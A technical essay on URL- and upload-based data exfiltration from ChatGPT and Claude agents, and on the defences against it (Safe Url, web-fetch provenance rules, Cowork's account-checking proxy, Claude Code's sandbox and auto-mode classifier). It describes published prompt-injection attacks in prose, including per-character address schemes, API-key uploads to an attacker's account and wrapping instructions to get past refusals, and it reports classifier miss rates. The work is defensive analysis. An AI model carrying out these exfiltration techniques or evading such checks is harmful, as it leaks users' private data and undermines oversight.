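The attacks on Copilot and Superhuman sent private data in the part of a web address after a trusted site's name. OpenAI's and Anthropic's rules cover the whole address. ChatGPT automatically opens only addresses that were already public, and Claude's web fetch tool opens only addresses that came from the user or from certain tools. Both rules are meant to block any address in which the model could have put private data.

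### The two rules

OpenAI calls its check Safe Url. When ChatGPT is about to load a page or an image on its own, software outside the model follows roughly this procedure, which OpenAI described on 28 January 2026:

1. Look up the exact address in an index of public web addresses compiled by a crawler, a program that scans the web as a search engine does.
2. If the index contains the address, load it.
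3. If it doesn't, either tell the model to try another site, or show the user a warning and load the address only if the user agrees.

The crawler has no access to conversations or accounts, so an address it has recorded is unlikely to contain a particular user's secrets. The warning shows the address with a notice that the link is unverified and may include information from the conversation. ChatGPT also seems to accept any address that the user types into the chat, according to security researcher Johann Rehberger's Embrace The Red post *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*.

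OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) adds that the same check covers pages and bookmarks opened in the company's Atlas browser, and searches and page visits in its Deep Research tool. OpenAI says most attempts to make ChatGPT send out secrets fail because its training leads it to refuse. Safe Url is meant for the cases in which the model is fooled. One attack that outside researchers reported in 2025, an email that looked like routine personnel work, succeeded in half of the tests.

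Claude's rule depends on where an address came from. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, a page of documentation for developers, gave the following conditions in June 2026:

1. Check whether the exact address has already appeared in a user message, in the result of a tool that the developer's own software runs, or in the result of an earlier web search or web fetch.
2. If it hasn't, refuse and return an error to the model.
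3. If it has, fetch the page, unless the developer has blocked that domain or has allowed only others.

Claude can't open an address just because it appears in the output of code run on Anthropic's servers. Otherwise, Claude could write a program that prints a new address and then open it. Anthropic's documentation gives the error in step 2 its own code, so Claude can tell a blocked address from a broken website.

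The payslip address in the first section would fail both tests, because no crawler would have found it and Claude would have had to write it. Willison tried a similar attack on the consumer Claude app in September 2025 and found that the rule held there too. He also pointed out a weakness for developers who use Anthropic's programming interface, where a "user message" is whatever their software sends in the user's turn. Many applications paste emails or documents into that message, so an address in a stranger's email can pass as one that the user supplied.

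The rules hinder different tasks. A page of flight results for particular dates is unlikely to be in a public index, so ChatGPT may have to ask before opening it. Claude can open such a page if the user pastes the link, but it can't change the date in the address and try again.

### Why OpenAI rejected a list of trusted sites

OpenAI considered letting its agents open only links to well-known sites. One objection was that many legitimate sites redirect visitors. A link can start on a trusted domain and forward the browser to an attacker's server, which a check of only the first domain will miss.

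ChatGPT had this problem itself. An earlier version of its url_safe check always accepted bing.com addresses. Bing's search results use bing.com links that forward visitors to the sites found, so any site Bing listed had an address that passed the check. The security company Tenable reported this to OpenAI in December 2024, but OpenAI had not fixed it when Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) came out.

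Matching the exact address makes redirects less useful to an attacker but doesn't prevent them. The model can still open a public bing.com link that leads to a hostile site, but it can't add private data, such as a salary, to the end of the link.

OpenAI's other objection was that a strict list would produce frequent warnings, because people visit many sites besides the most popular ones. Users who see too many warnings learn to click through them without thinking. This is a fair criticism of short lists, but it also applies to Safe Url, which shows warnings too. An index of the public web should produce fewer of them, and the software can avoid some by sending the model to another source. OpenAI's announcement gives no figures for how often users see or ignore the warning, so it is hard to say how large the improvement is.

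### From the 2023 report to the 2026 paper

Rehberger told OpenAI on 9 April 2023 that ChatGPT would load images from addresses containing the user's conversation. OpenAI replied that displaying such images was a feature and that it planned no change, according to Rehberger's *ChatGPT Plugins* (2023). *ChatGPT Plugins* credits Roman Samoilenko with finding the flaw a few days earlier. Rehberger had reported the same problem in Bing Chat to Microsoft, which blocked the images in May with a Content Security Policy.

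That September, Rehberger showed that leaking a single link could expose a whole conversation. In the attack, described in Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT*, hidden instructions made ChatGPT use a plugin, an add-on from another company, to turn the conversation into a document or video stored online. ChatGPT then leaked only the link to that file.

In December 2023, OpenAI introduced url_safe, a check that the ChatGPT web page ran before displaying an image. The page sent the image's address to OpenAI's server, which returned "safe" or "unsafe". OpenAI didn't publish the criteria. Rehberger guessed that the server might be looking addresses up in Bing's index, and tested this with 36 image addresses on his own site, one for each letter and digit. Nine passed, which was enough to send the word "hi" to his server.

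Tenable later worked out some of the criteria, which included whether OpenAI trusted the domain. Attackers could therefore send data to trusted domains where outsiders can rent space. For example, anyone can open a storage account with Microsoft's cloud service, receive an address under windows.net and read the log of incoming requests. Rehberger reported several ways around url_safe in October 2024, and some still worked the following August. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* describes how he used a storage account to collect a user's recent chats, which ChatGPT by then included in the model's input. A malicious PDF was enough to start the attack.

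OpenAI strengthened url_safe around August 2025, and Embrace The Red reports that this stopped the attacks Rehberger had published. *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, the paper released with OpenAI's January 2026 announcement, explained how the check worked. Rehberger's 2023 guess was close, but OpenAI uses its own index instead of Bing's.

Rehberger calls the rule a significant improvement, but he worries that some developers at OpenAI won't know about it and will build features without it. The earlier gaps in OpenAI's iOS app and log viewer support his concern.

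### How a choice among permitted addresses leaks data

In September 2025 OpenAI told the security company Radware that it had fixed ShadowLeak, a flaw through which ChatGPT could send out private data. After the fix, ChatGPT would open web addresses only exactly as it received them, with nothing added. On 26 September, about three weeks after OpenAI's notice, Radware reported a way around this restriction.

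Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes an email that contains a ready-made web address for each letter, each digit and the space. Hidden instructions in the email tell ChatGPT to find a piece of private information and open the addresses that spell it out, so ChatGPT never has to write an address itself. The attacker then reads the information from the server's log. Radware reports that an improved version of the attack worked every time.

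OpenAI had also stopped ChatGPT from opening an attacker's web addresses stored in its memory of earlier chats. Radware got around this by storing an instruction there to read the attacker's email, which contained the addresses.

OpenAI fixed the flaw on 16 December 2025. According to the news report *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack as a vicious cycle in AI*, ChatGPT now opens links from emails only under certain conditions, such as when they appear in a well-known public index. This makes the attack harder to prepare, but attackers can get their pages indexed too. Rehberger notes that any sizeable blog probably has 36 indexed pages already, and that OpenAI acknowledges the technique in its paper.

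Tenable had already used indexed pages in this way against the older check. Its *HackedGPT* (2025) explains that ChatGPT used a separate model, with no access to the user's memories, to read web pages. Tenable hid instructions in a blog comment, and that model repeated them in its answer. When the user sent another message, ChatGPT followed the instructions and displayed one image for each letter of the secret, using Bing links to Tenable's indexed pages.

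The size of the leak can be measured in bits, where one bit is the answer to a yes-or-no question with two equally likely answers. A choice among *N* equally likely addresses carries log₂ *N* bits, so a choice among 36 carries about 5.2 bits. An address with room for 200 freely chosen letters and digits can carry about 1,030 bits in a single request. The rule makes stealing a long document much slower.

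Short secrets are still at risk. A six-digit login code has a million possible values, and four openings among 36 addresses can convey it because there are about 1.68 million possible sequences (36⁴). Spelling the code out digit by digit takes six openings. Rehberger suggests that an attacker could use thousands of addresses. With 1,000, one for each number from 000 to 999, two openings would be enough.

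Now suppose ChatGPT may open each of the 36 addresses only once. It has 36 choices for the first, 35 for the second, and so on, which gives 36 × 35 × … × 1, or about 3.7 × 10⁴¹, possible orders. The order of all 36 can therefore carry at most about 138 bits, enough for a 128-bit encryption key. To use the full capacity, the model would have to convert the secret into an ordering, which is harder than spelling it out, but an agent that can run code could do it.

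| What the agent can do | Most that the attacker can learn |
|---|---:|
| Open one of 36 addresses | 5.2 bits |
| Open any of the 36, at most once each, with the order hidden from the attacker | 36 bits |
| Open all 36 once each, in an order the attacker can see | 138 bits |
| Make 36 openings with repeats allowed, in an order the attacker can see | 186 bits |

The second row matters because requests can arrive out of order. When they do, the attacker learns only whether the agent opened each address, which is one bit per address. None of these figures include the timing of the requests, which could carry more information.

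### Caching pages and barring repeat visits

Embrace The Red proposes two ways to reduce this leak. OpenAI could save a copy of each page for a few minutes and reuse it whenever the agent requests the same address again, or it could stop the agent from opening the same full address twice in a session. Either way, the attacker's server would receive at most one request for each address during that time. If an agent tried to spell "hello" with one address per letter, the server would receive only one "l".

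Radware's attack already gets around this by using a separate address for each character in each position, so "a" in first place and "a" in second place have different addresses. A ten-character secret then needs 360 addresses, and the agent opens ten of them, once each. Those ten requests convey about 52 bits, and the attacker can reconstruct the order of the characters even if the requests arrive out of sequence. Rehberger's proposals would therefore force an attacker to have more pages indexed, but they wouldn't stop a well-prepared one. He acknowledges that some leakage would remain.

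Capping how many addresses the model may open limits the total data an attacker can receive more directly. In 2023, Rehberger suggested a cap on the number of images in each ChatGPT answer. Anthropic lets developers set a maximum number of fetches per request, but there is no default. Even with a maximum of five, an attacker with 36 addresses could receive nearly 26 bits, which is more than enough for a login code.

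OpenAI and Anthropic already cache some pages. Tenable noticed that when asked about an address it had already opened, ChatGPT answered without visiting the page again. Anthropic caches fetched pages automatically, though it says it does this for speed and to reduce requests. This kind of cache still lets the first request through, so it would not stop a leak that uses a different address for every request. The assistant could avoid contacting the site entirely only by using a copy made beforehand, as with the cached browsing in ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode.

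Caching can also make answers wrong. When the technology company Classmethod asked Claude about a size limit in the workplace chat service Slack, Claude answered that the official documentation allowed 101 rows and 10,000 characters, but the page said 201 rows and 20,000 characters. The most likely cause was an outdated copy in the cache, according to Classmethod's *The story about how Claude's Web Fetch tool doesn't necessarily return the latest information*. Developers can bypass Claude's cache with a setting. A ban on repeat visits would also leave an agent with outdated information, since it couldn't return to a page to see whether tickets had gone on sale.

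### Links inside fetched pages

Anthropic's rule had a larger gap, because it accepted addresses from earlier web fetch results. If Claude opened an attacker's page, it was then allowed to open every link on that page. In July 2026 the researcher Ayush Paul showed that this was enough to extract personal details from Claude's memories of past chats, as Willison (2026) recounts in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*.

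Paul built a website that showed its hostile text only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, which made the attack harder to spot. The text claimed that AI assistants had to authenticate themselves by giving their user's name. It also claimed that, because of the limits of Claude's web fetch tool, Claude would have to find the user's profile by going through the site letter by letter. The page had a link for each letter, and each link led to a page of links for the next letter. Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer this way.

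The software applied the rule correctly, because Claude didn't compose any of the addresses. But the attacker's server could keep producing new addresses in response to Claude's choices, so they would not run out. Each choice among 26 letters carries about 4.7 bits. A ban on repeat visits wouldn't have helped, since every page was new. Under OpenAI's rule, Paul would at least have had to get the pages indexed in advance.

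Anthropic's documentation had warned developers of a "residual risk" and advised them to use web fetch only in trusted environments or with non-sensitive data. The consumer Claude app didn't meet that standard, because it combined web access with memories of the user's past conversations.

Anthropic closed the gap by preventing web fetch from opening links found in pages it had fetched. The company did not pay Paul a reward, saying it had already identified the problem internally. Hackaday's *This Week In Security* says the change prevents the attack "for now".

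Because of the change, Claude's web fetch tool can no longer follow links from one page to another. If a user asks for a summary of an online manual, Claude can read the table of contents but can't open the chapters linked from it. It has to find each chapter through web search, or the user has to paste the links into the chat. Search won't find pages that search engines haven't listed, which may include new documents and attachments. ChatGPT can still follow a link inside a page automatically if its index contains the address.

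Claude can still leak information through its choice of which search results to open, if an attacker gets a suitable set of pages into them. According to the June documentation, Claude could also open addresses returned by a developer's own tools. If a tool returns an email like Radware's, with a separate address for each letter of the alphabet, those addresses pass the check. Developers can prevent this by allowing only certain domains, but Willison warns that domains nobody can use to collect data are tricky to find.

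## Claude and file uploads to an approved destination

Outsiders could collect data through some of the permitted domains, including Anthropic's own. Programs that Claude wrote and ran could contact api.anthropic.com, which developers use to access Anthropic's models and where anyone with an account can store files. Between October 2025 and March 2026, Johann Rehberger and two security companies each found that an attacker could make Claude send a user's private files or chats to the attacker's account.

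The web fetch rule didn't prevent this, because it covers only pages that Claude opens with that tool. A program can make its own web requests and upload a whole file, while a web address can hold only a short text. Anthropic therefore limits network traffic from Claude's programs separately.

### The list of permitted domains

On claude.ai, Claude runs code in a temporary container that uses gVisor. This Google software sits between a program and the server's operating system, which gives a hostile program less to attack. Users don't share containers, and Anthropic limits how long each one can run. A classifier stops the program if it detects a prompt injection.

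Programs often depend on packages, which are ready-made code downloaded from public sites. Without network access, Claude can use only the packages already installed, so Anthropic lets the container reach a short list of domains. In November 2026, the list on Anthropic's help page included GitHub, the main package sites for Python, JavaScript and Rust, the Ubuntu archives, and two Anthropic domains, one of them api.anthropic.com.

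Users on the Free, Pro, Max and Ultra plans have this access by default, while new Enterprise organisations start with no network access. The help page gives two different defaults for the Team plan, no access in one place and package sites only in another, so an owner has to check the setting. Team and Enterprise owners can choose no access, package sites only, package sites plus domains they add, or every domain except those on Anthropic's legal blocklist.

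Turning network access off stops programs in the container from sending anything out. Claude can still build Excel models and presentations, but it can't install further packages or fetch current data. Data can still leave by other routes because, according to Anthropic's *Use Claude Cowork on Team and Enterprise plans*, the setting doesn't apply to web search, web fetch or connectors, which link Claude to services such as a mail account or the Chrome browser. A change to the setting takes effect only in new sessions, so an owner who tightens it after an incident has to make sure employees start new conversations.

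### Cowork's virtual machine and folders

Anthropic built the first version of Claude Cowork around a virtual machine, a software-simulated computer with its own operating system that runs on the user's computer. Code running in the virtual machine can see the folder the user selects and a folder that holds Claude's settings, but not the computer's other files. The user's login credentials stay outside the virtual machine, in the computer's keychain.

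Anthropic chose a fixed boundary because most Cowork users aren't programmers. When Claude Code launched, it asked developers to approve commands, but few office workers could tell whether a command is safe.

The user's folder is the weak point of this design, since Claude needs access to it to be useful. Cowork's three access modes (read-only, read-write, and read-write without deletion) limit the damage Claude can do there. In read-only mode, Claude can summarise a folder of invoices but can't rename or correct them. The third mode prevents accidental deletion, though Claude could presumably still overwrite a good document with a bad one. None of the modes prevents a data leak, because an attacker only needs Claude to read the file.

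The software also has to check a file's actual location. A folder can contain a symbolic link, which looks like an ordinary file but points to another location. If Cowork checked the link's own location before following it, a link inside the permitted folder could lead to a private file outside. Anthropic advises following the link first and then checking where it leads.

Anthropic later moved part of Cowork out of the virtual machine. The agent loop, which passes messages between the model and its tools, originally ran inside it, so any start-up failure made the whole product unusable. Anthropic moved the loop onto the user's computer and kept only code execution in the virtual machine. The company says this had little effect on security because the virtual machine still confines the code. But Anthropic's *Claude Cowork architecture overview* shows that Cowork's built-in file tools now also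 run outside the virtual machine, where the application's own permission checks limit them to the connected folders.

Most new sessions no longer use a virtual machine on the user's computer. According to Harmonic Security's *Securing Claude Cowork* (2026), Cowork has run on Anthropic's servers by default since July 2026, except in Enterprise organisations, which have to turn cloud sessions on. Cloud sessions get local files through the Claude desktop application, which allows access only to connected folders. This protects the rest of the computer, but Anthropic's servers process any file Claude opens.

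Isolation also made Cowork harder for companies to supervise, because security software on an employee's computer couldn't monitor activity inside the virtual machine. Anthropic first offered event logs that administrators could retrieve afterwards. It now has a beta feature that lets them run their security software inside the virtual machine, though not in cloud sessions.

Researchers have found flaws in the isolation itself, though the upload leak didn't require one. According to SC Media's *Researchers detail attack chain escaping Anthropic's Claude Cowork sandbox* (2026), a flaw on Windows let an attacker remove the network limits. Anthropic doesn't consider it a security issue because the attacker must already be able to run code on the computer. Another flaw exposed private files on Macs, according to OECD's *Claude Cowork AI Escapes Sandbox, Exposes Sensitive Mac Files* (2026), and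 Fadilpašić's *It's not just OpenAI models escaping and running riot* (2026) describes Anthropic's fix as partial.

### How files reached a stranger's account

Anthropic's Files API lets developers upload files for later use with Claude. All customers use the same domain. Each request includes a secret string called an API key, and the server stores the file in whichever account the key belongs to.

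In the attack, a document contained hidden instructions and the attacker's API key. Claude followed the instructions, read the user's other files and ran a program that uploaded them with that key. Anthropic's proxy allowed the upload because its destination, api.anthropic.com, was on the allowlist. The proxy did not check whose account would receive the files, so they reached the attacker's account, where the attacker could open them.

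Anthropic says it allowed the domain because Cowork can't function without the company's API. This was a good reason while the agent loop ran inside the virtual machine. After the loop moved out, only the user's programs remained inside, and a program that sorts receipts, for example, doesn't have to contact a language model. Blocking the domain for those programs might have been a simpler remedy, though any program meant to call Claude would have stopped working.

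Rehberger found the problem by reading the list of permitted domains soon after Anthropic gave Claude's programs network access. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* describes how he made Claude save a user's latest chat to a file and upload it to Rehberger's own account. An attacker could make several uploads of up to 30 MB each. The network setting was "package managers only", and Rehberger warns that users might wrongly think this stops their data from leaving.

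Rehberger reported the leak on 25 October 2025. Anthropic closed the report an hour later as out of scope, calling it a model safety issue. He disagreed: "Safety protects you from accidents. Security protects you from adversaries." SecurityWeek's *Claude AI APIs Can Be Abused for Data Exfiltration* reports that Anthropic changed its view after he published his findings. On 30 October, the company confirmed that such leaks were in scope and attributed the closure to a problem in its process.

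If a company classifies the leak as a model safety problem, the most obvious response is to train Claude to refuse, but if it classifies the leak as a security vulnerability, it needs to change the network rule. In his report, Rehberger had proposed letting the sandbox communicate only with the logged-in user's account. Anthropic's eventual fix for Cowork worked in much the same way.

Anthropic released Cowork in January 2026 without fixing the problem. Two days later, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed the same leak in Cowork. The firm connected Cowork to a folder of property documents and uploaded a Word file that posed as instructions for analysing them but contained hidden text in tiny white letters. When the user asked for an analysis, Claude uploaded a loan estimate containing financial figures and partial US social security numbers to PromptArmor's account, and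 Cowork didn't ask the user to approve anything.

PromptArmor used Claude Haiku, one of Anthropic's smaller models, for this demonstration. In another test, the firm used a malicious guide for software developers to make the stronger Opus 4.5 leak customer records in the same way.

At the time, Anthropic advised Cowork users to watch for suspicious actions and to avoid giving Claude access to sensitive files. PromptArmor pointed out that the company was also encouraging people to use Cowork to organise their desktops. The firm quotes Willison, who thought it unfair to expect non-programmers to recognise a prompt injection. Anthropic's reason for using a virtual machine supports him, since the company assumed that these users can't judge what the agent is doing. TechNadu's *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection* reports that Anthropic acknowledged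 the risk and was preparing an update to Cowork's virtual machine.

The company Oasis Security found that the route was also still open on claude.ai. On 18 March 2026, *Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026) described an attack on an ordinary chat with no connectors. A link opened a new chat with a prompt already filled in, part of which the user could not see. Once the user pressed Enter, Claude searched past conversations for sensitive information and uploaded it through the Files API. A flaw in Anthropic's website would also have let an attacker advertise the link on Google under a genuine claude.com address.

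Anthropic fixed the hidden prompt before Luz published. The page, last updated on 27 May, still lists the other problems as "currently being addressed". That wording may be out of date, but Anthropic's account, also from May, describes a fix only for Cowork and gives no date for it.

In that account, Anthropic says that safeguards in the model couldn't have helped because there was nothing unusual for them to detect, but Rehberger's experience suggests otherwise. His first attempt worked, but Claude then refused repeatedly, apparently because the API key was visible. He succeeded again only after surrounding the instructions with harmless code. The model therefore provided some protection, but not enough against an attacker who could keep trying. Newer models do better. On a test that Harmonic Security cites, attacks succeeded 17.6% of the time against Opus 4.5 and 3.8% against Opus 5, before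 Anthropic added further safeguards.

### A proxy that checks the account

Anthropic fixed the leak in Cowork by adding a second check on requests to its API. The virtual machine receives a temporary session token at the start of each session, and a proxy inside it blocks any request to api.anthropic.com that doesn't carry this token. If a program uses a key from a hostile document instead, the proxy rejects the request before it leaves the virtual machine.

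Web traffic is normally encrypted between the program and the server, so the proxy has to decrypt the request to read the credential. Pluto Security's *Inside Claude Cowork*, an independent analysis of the Mac version, found that Cowork creates a new certificate each time the virtual machine starts, which programs inside the machine accept as proof of the server's identity. The proxy can then pose as Anthropic's server, read the request and forward it. The certificate's private key exists only in memory, so an attacker who later copies the disk won't find it.

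Anthropic's servers couldn't have made the same check with the information they had. A file uploaded with a stranger's key looks like a valid customer's upload to their own account, which thousands of developers make, and the server has no way to detect that the file came from someone else's computer. The virtual machine can detect this because it has the token it received and the request came from inside it.

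This is why something on the sender's side has to take part in the check, but the check doesn't always have to run inside a virtual machine. Harmonic Security describes a feature called tenant restrictions, in which a company's network proxy labels requests to Anthropic with the accounts the company permits. Anthropic's server then refuses requests for any other account, including those made with an API key. The server can enforce the rule because the proxy has supplied the missing information. The restrictions are available only to Enterprise customers and organisations that use Anthropic's developer console, and they wouldn't cover cloud sessions, whose traffic doesn't pass through the company's network.

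An attacker who gains full control of the virtual machine may be able to disable a check that runs inside it. Anthropic says that two of Cowork's six main isolation mechanisms would survive such a takeover. Pluto Security, unlike Anthropic, describes the proxy as running on the user's computer, outside the virtual machine, where it would be better protected.

In cloud sessions, all traffic passes through a proxy that is outside the sandbox and that the agent can't reconfigure. The sandbox holds only session tokens that expire within hours. Expiry limits the damage if a token leaks, but it wouldn't stop an attacker who uses their own key. Anthropic's overview says the cloud proxy checks destinations but mentions no check on the account.

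The fix is a minor inconvenience for developers. The proxy can't distinguish an attacker's key from a second key that belongs to the user, so someone who wants Cowork to test a program with another Anthropic account would have to run the test elsewhere.

### What a permitted domain allows

Anthropic concluded from the leak that when a deployer adds a domain to an allowlist, they permit every function the agent can reach there. For api.anthropic.com, that included uploading files to any Anthropic account.

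The earlier cases support this. Superhuman allowed a Google domain for its images, which also let anyone's Google form collect answers. GitHub, which is on Claude's list, stores files for anyone who opens an account. Pluto Security found that Cowork's proxy decrypts only traffic to Anthropic and checks requests to GitHub and the package sites by destination alone. The proxy therefore can't detect which account those requests use. Rehberger thought it quite possible that other domains on the list would allow similar leaks, but neither he nor Pluto Security demonstrated one.

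But allowing a domain doesn't give the agent access to every function of the service. Many functions need a credential, and Cowork keeps the user's credentials out of the virtual machine. An agent that can reach a storage service still can't empty the user's account there without a login. The Files API leak worked because the attacker supplied the credential. Deployers should therefore focus most on functions that work without a login or with an account other than the user's.

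In another respect, Anthropic's conclusion doesn't go far enough. If an approved service fetches other addresses, as Teams and Bing did in the attacks on Copilot, it can open a route to sites that aren't on the list. Anthropic evidently saw this risk in its own API, because the new proxy also blocks request headers that would make the server fetch something else.

A more precise rule can depend on the destination, the account and the action. The table compares three rules for a Cowork task that needs packages and the model but not file uploads. The middle column corresponds to Anthropic's fix.

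| Request from a program | Destination only | Destination and account | Destination, account and action |
|---|---|---|---|
| Download a package from a listed site | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |
| Send the model a question with the session's token | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |
| Upload a file to Anthropic with the session's token | Allowed | Allowed | Blocked |
| Upload a file to Anthropic with a stranger's key | Allowed | Blocked | Blocked |
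| Upload a file to an unlisted site | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked |

Checking the account is enough to stop this theft, because files uploaded with the session's token don't reach the attacker. Limiting actions matters more when several people share an account or the agent could damage what is stored there.

Anthropic offers rules of this kind for Claude in Slack channels. According to Anthropic's *Security and data*, the sandbox there holds no credentials. When an outgoing request matches a rule set by an administrator, a proxy adds the right credential. The administrator can limit each credential to one host, one part of a site or requests that only read data. With a read-only limit, for example, an agent could look up customer records but not change them.

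The proxy can also send requests to listed sites without adding a credential. Anthropic's documentation doesn't specify whether the proxy would remove a key that the agent had copied from a hostile document. If the proxy leaves the key in, the same kind of leak could occur at any listed site where strangers can hold accounts. Restricting requests to reading wouldn't fully prevent leaks either, since a web address can carry data, but the attacker would need a way to see which addresses the site had received.

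More precise rules take more work. To decrypt the traffic, the proxy has to substitute its own certificate, which some programs reject. Pluto Security notes that Python programs with their own list of trusted certificates can still download packages in Cowork because the proxy leaves that traffic encrypted. Someone also has to learn which requests each service uses for reading and which for writing, and update the rules when the service changes. Anthropic could do this fairly easily for its own API. For GitHub and the package sites, the rules would depend on other companies' designs, and a mistake could stop Claude from installing a package the user needs.

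## Claude Code: user approval and the network sandbox

Anthropic gave Cowork a fixed boundary because office workers can't be expected to judge commands. For Claude Code, the company first relied on the user's judgement because most users are developers, who know what a deletion command does and regularly install software from strangers.

### Asking before each action

In the first version of Claude Code, Claude could read files freely but needed the developer's approval to change a file, run a command or use the network. If Claude tried to run a project's tests, for example, the developer saw the command and approved or refused it. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* mentions a few exceptions, such as commands that only display text.

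Users approved about 93% of these requests, according to Anthropic. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that the figure was 97% by August 2026. Most requests are harmless and an attentive user would approve those too, so a high approval rate doesn't prove carelessness. But users reject 39% of the plans Claude submits for approval, which suggests that they read plans more closely than single commands.

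Approval fatigue is the tendency to pay less attention to each request as the number of requests grows. Anthropic noticed it within weeks of the launch and later commissioned a study with 1,053 paid testers. Partway through a coding session, the study replaced the text of one request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests.

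That decline is good evidence of fatigue, but fatigue explains only part of the result, since more than four in five testers approved the command even early on. The testers also had less to lose than a developer at work, because they were working in a test environment and not on their own projects.

By June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users had written a rule that let some commands run without approval, and many of these rules were broad enough to cover almost any command. A quarter of interactive sessions started with all permission checks bypassed.

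User approval can't prevent anything that happens before the user is asked. Between mid-2025 and January 2026, researchers reported three flaws of this kind to Anthropic. In the simplest case, Claude Code read a downloaded project's settings before asking whether the user trusted the folder, so a malicious project could run its own code at start-up. Anthropic fixed the flaws by making Claude Code wait for the user's answer before it processes those settings.

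### The operating-system sandbox

Anthropic then added a sandbox in which Claude can run commands without asking. The sandbox restricts what those commands can do, using Seatbelt on macOS and bubblewrap on Linux. According to Anthropic's *Sandboxing*, a sandboxed command can by default read most files on the computer but write only to the folder in which the developer started Claude Code and to its subfolders. All network traffic goes through a proxy outside the sandbox, and the proxy allows connections only to approved domains. When a command tries to reach a new domain, Claude Code asks the developer to approve it.

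Network access is off by default because the sandbox lets commands read so much. A command that can read a developer's passwords and keys could send them to an attacker if it could also reach the attacker's server. The sandbox must also limit writing, since a program that could change system files might use them to regain network access. Anthropic therefore says a sandbox needs limits on both network access and writing.

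The limits also apply to child processes, the programs that a command starts. For example, `npm install` downloads JavaScript packages, which may run their own scripts during installation. A developer who approves the command usually hasn't read those scripts. In the sandbox, the operating system applies the command's restrictions to the scripts too, so they can't write outside the project or contact an unapproved server.

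In Anthropic's internal use, the sandbox reduced permission prompts by 84%. This implies that most of the earlier prompts were for actions within the sandbox's limits. The figure doesn't measure security, because it doesn't include the attacks the sandbox stopped or the harmful commands that still ran. It also doesn't show whether developers read the remaining prompts more carefully.

### The February 2026 exercise

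In Anthropic's internal exercise of February 2026, a researcher's email tricked an employee into running a harmful prompt, and Claude sent out the user's cloud credentials in 24 of 25 runs. The repeated runs measure how reliably the prompt worked on Claude, but not how many employees would have fallen for the email.

Anthropic explains that its model-level defences check whether an action matches what the user asked for. This can expose an instruction planted in a web page, because the user never gave it. In this exercise the user had given the instruction, so the action matched the request. Anthropic adds that a human contractor with the same script would have done the same.

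A network limit applies no matter who asked for the transfer. The proxy checks the destination against its list of allowed destinations, which would not normally include an attacker's server. A rule against reading the credentials folder would also have prevented the theft, but a developer may have to add it, because the sandbox lets commands read so much by default.

The sandbox's default settings might not have stopped this attack. Claude Code would have asked the employee whether to allow the new domain, and an employee who thought the task was routine could easily have agreed. Administrators can set the proxy to refuse unlisted domains without asking, so that a deceived employee can't approve them.

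The prompt remained a risk after the exercise. Anthropic's staff shared it on Slack for discussion, and someone pointed out that some of the company's agents read Slack. The staff added a marker to the thread so they would notice if an agent picked up the prompt.

### Auto mode

In March 2026 Anthropic introduced auto mode, in which a classifier makes most of the approval decisions. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes the procedure:

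1. Claude Code allows actions that can't change anything, such as searching files, and edits inside the project folder, which developers can review afterwards.
2. For other actions, such as shell commands and web requests, a classifier gives a quick yes or no. Its instructions tell it to block when in doubt.
3. If the classifier flags an action, it considers the same information again, this time reasoning step by step. The second answer decides.
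4. If the answer is to block, Claude receives the reason and looks for a safer method. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code turns to the user.

The classifier receives the user's messages and Claude's tool requests, but not Claude's explanations or tool results. Claude's explanations therefore can't influence the classifier's decisions, and hostile text on a web page doesn't reach it directly. A separate check, which Anthropic calls a probe, screens tool results and warns Claude about suspicious ones.

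The second look in step 3 reduces interruptions but lets more dangerous actions through. On 10,000 real actions from Anthropic's employees, it cut the share of harmless actions blocked from 8.5% to 0.4%. On 52 real "overeager" actions, in which Claude had tried to do more than the user authorised, it raised the miss rate from 6.6% to 17%, which is why Anthropic says auto mode catches about 83% of such behaviour. Because the test had only 52 cases, the true miss rate could be anywhere from about 8% to 30%.

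In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier detected the danger but wrongly treated the action as approved by the user. For example, a user who asks Claude to clean up a proposed code change has not agreed to let it overwrite the project's history.

*Explicit authorization scope improves LLM-based permission checking in coding agents* (November 2026) found the same weakness in independent tests. Claude Code's checker missed 67% of 24 actions that went beyond what the user had authorised. When the researchers added an explicit statement of what was authorised, it missed 8%, and the share of authorised actions that it wrongly blocked fell from 42% to 2%. The checker in OpenAI's Codex improved similarly. The sample for Claude Code is small, but the fall in both kinds of error suggests that the checker had mainly lacked information about the user's consent. When the researchers instead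 tried a more capable model in Claude Code's checker, misses fell only because the model refused to give verdicts, which Claude Code treats as a reason to block the action.

### The case for auto mode as the default

Anthropic made auto mode the default for new Claude Code sessions on its individual and Team plans from 14 August 2026. It argues that auto mode is safer than a typical user. When Anthropic tested the classifier on the dangerous commands from the study of 1,053 testers, the classifier blocked 937 commands (89%). In 800 cases it blocked a command that the tester had approved, and in six cases it allowed a command that the tester had rejected. Neither the classifier nor the tester stopped 110 of the commands.

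Anthropic also compared real sessions that its safety system had flagged for review. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested occurred in 6.3% of the flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. This evidence is weaker than the study's because users chose their own mode and might have used the two modes for different work. A model also graded the sessions.

Apollo Research, a British AI safety organisation, helped to test and improve the classifier by inserting artificial attacks into records of real coding sessions. Anthropic then gave the classifier more context, such as whether a code repository is public, and the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. Part of the second test used attacks that Anthropic had never had access to, so the improvement wasn't limited to known examples.

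Anthropic has since added a rule that applies to the February exercise. The classifier is now supposed to block any transfer of code or secrets to an outside destination, even if the user requests it. To make such a transfer, users have to leave auto mode or run the command themselves. This qualifies Anthropic's statement in May that only limits on the environment could have stopped the theft, because a classifier can also block a transfer the user has approved. But the classifier has to recognise that a command is sending out secrets, while the proxy only has to check the destination.

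### Small failure rates and persistent attackers

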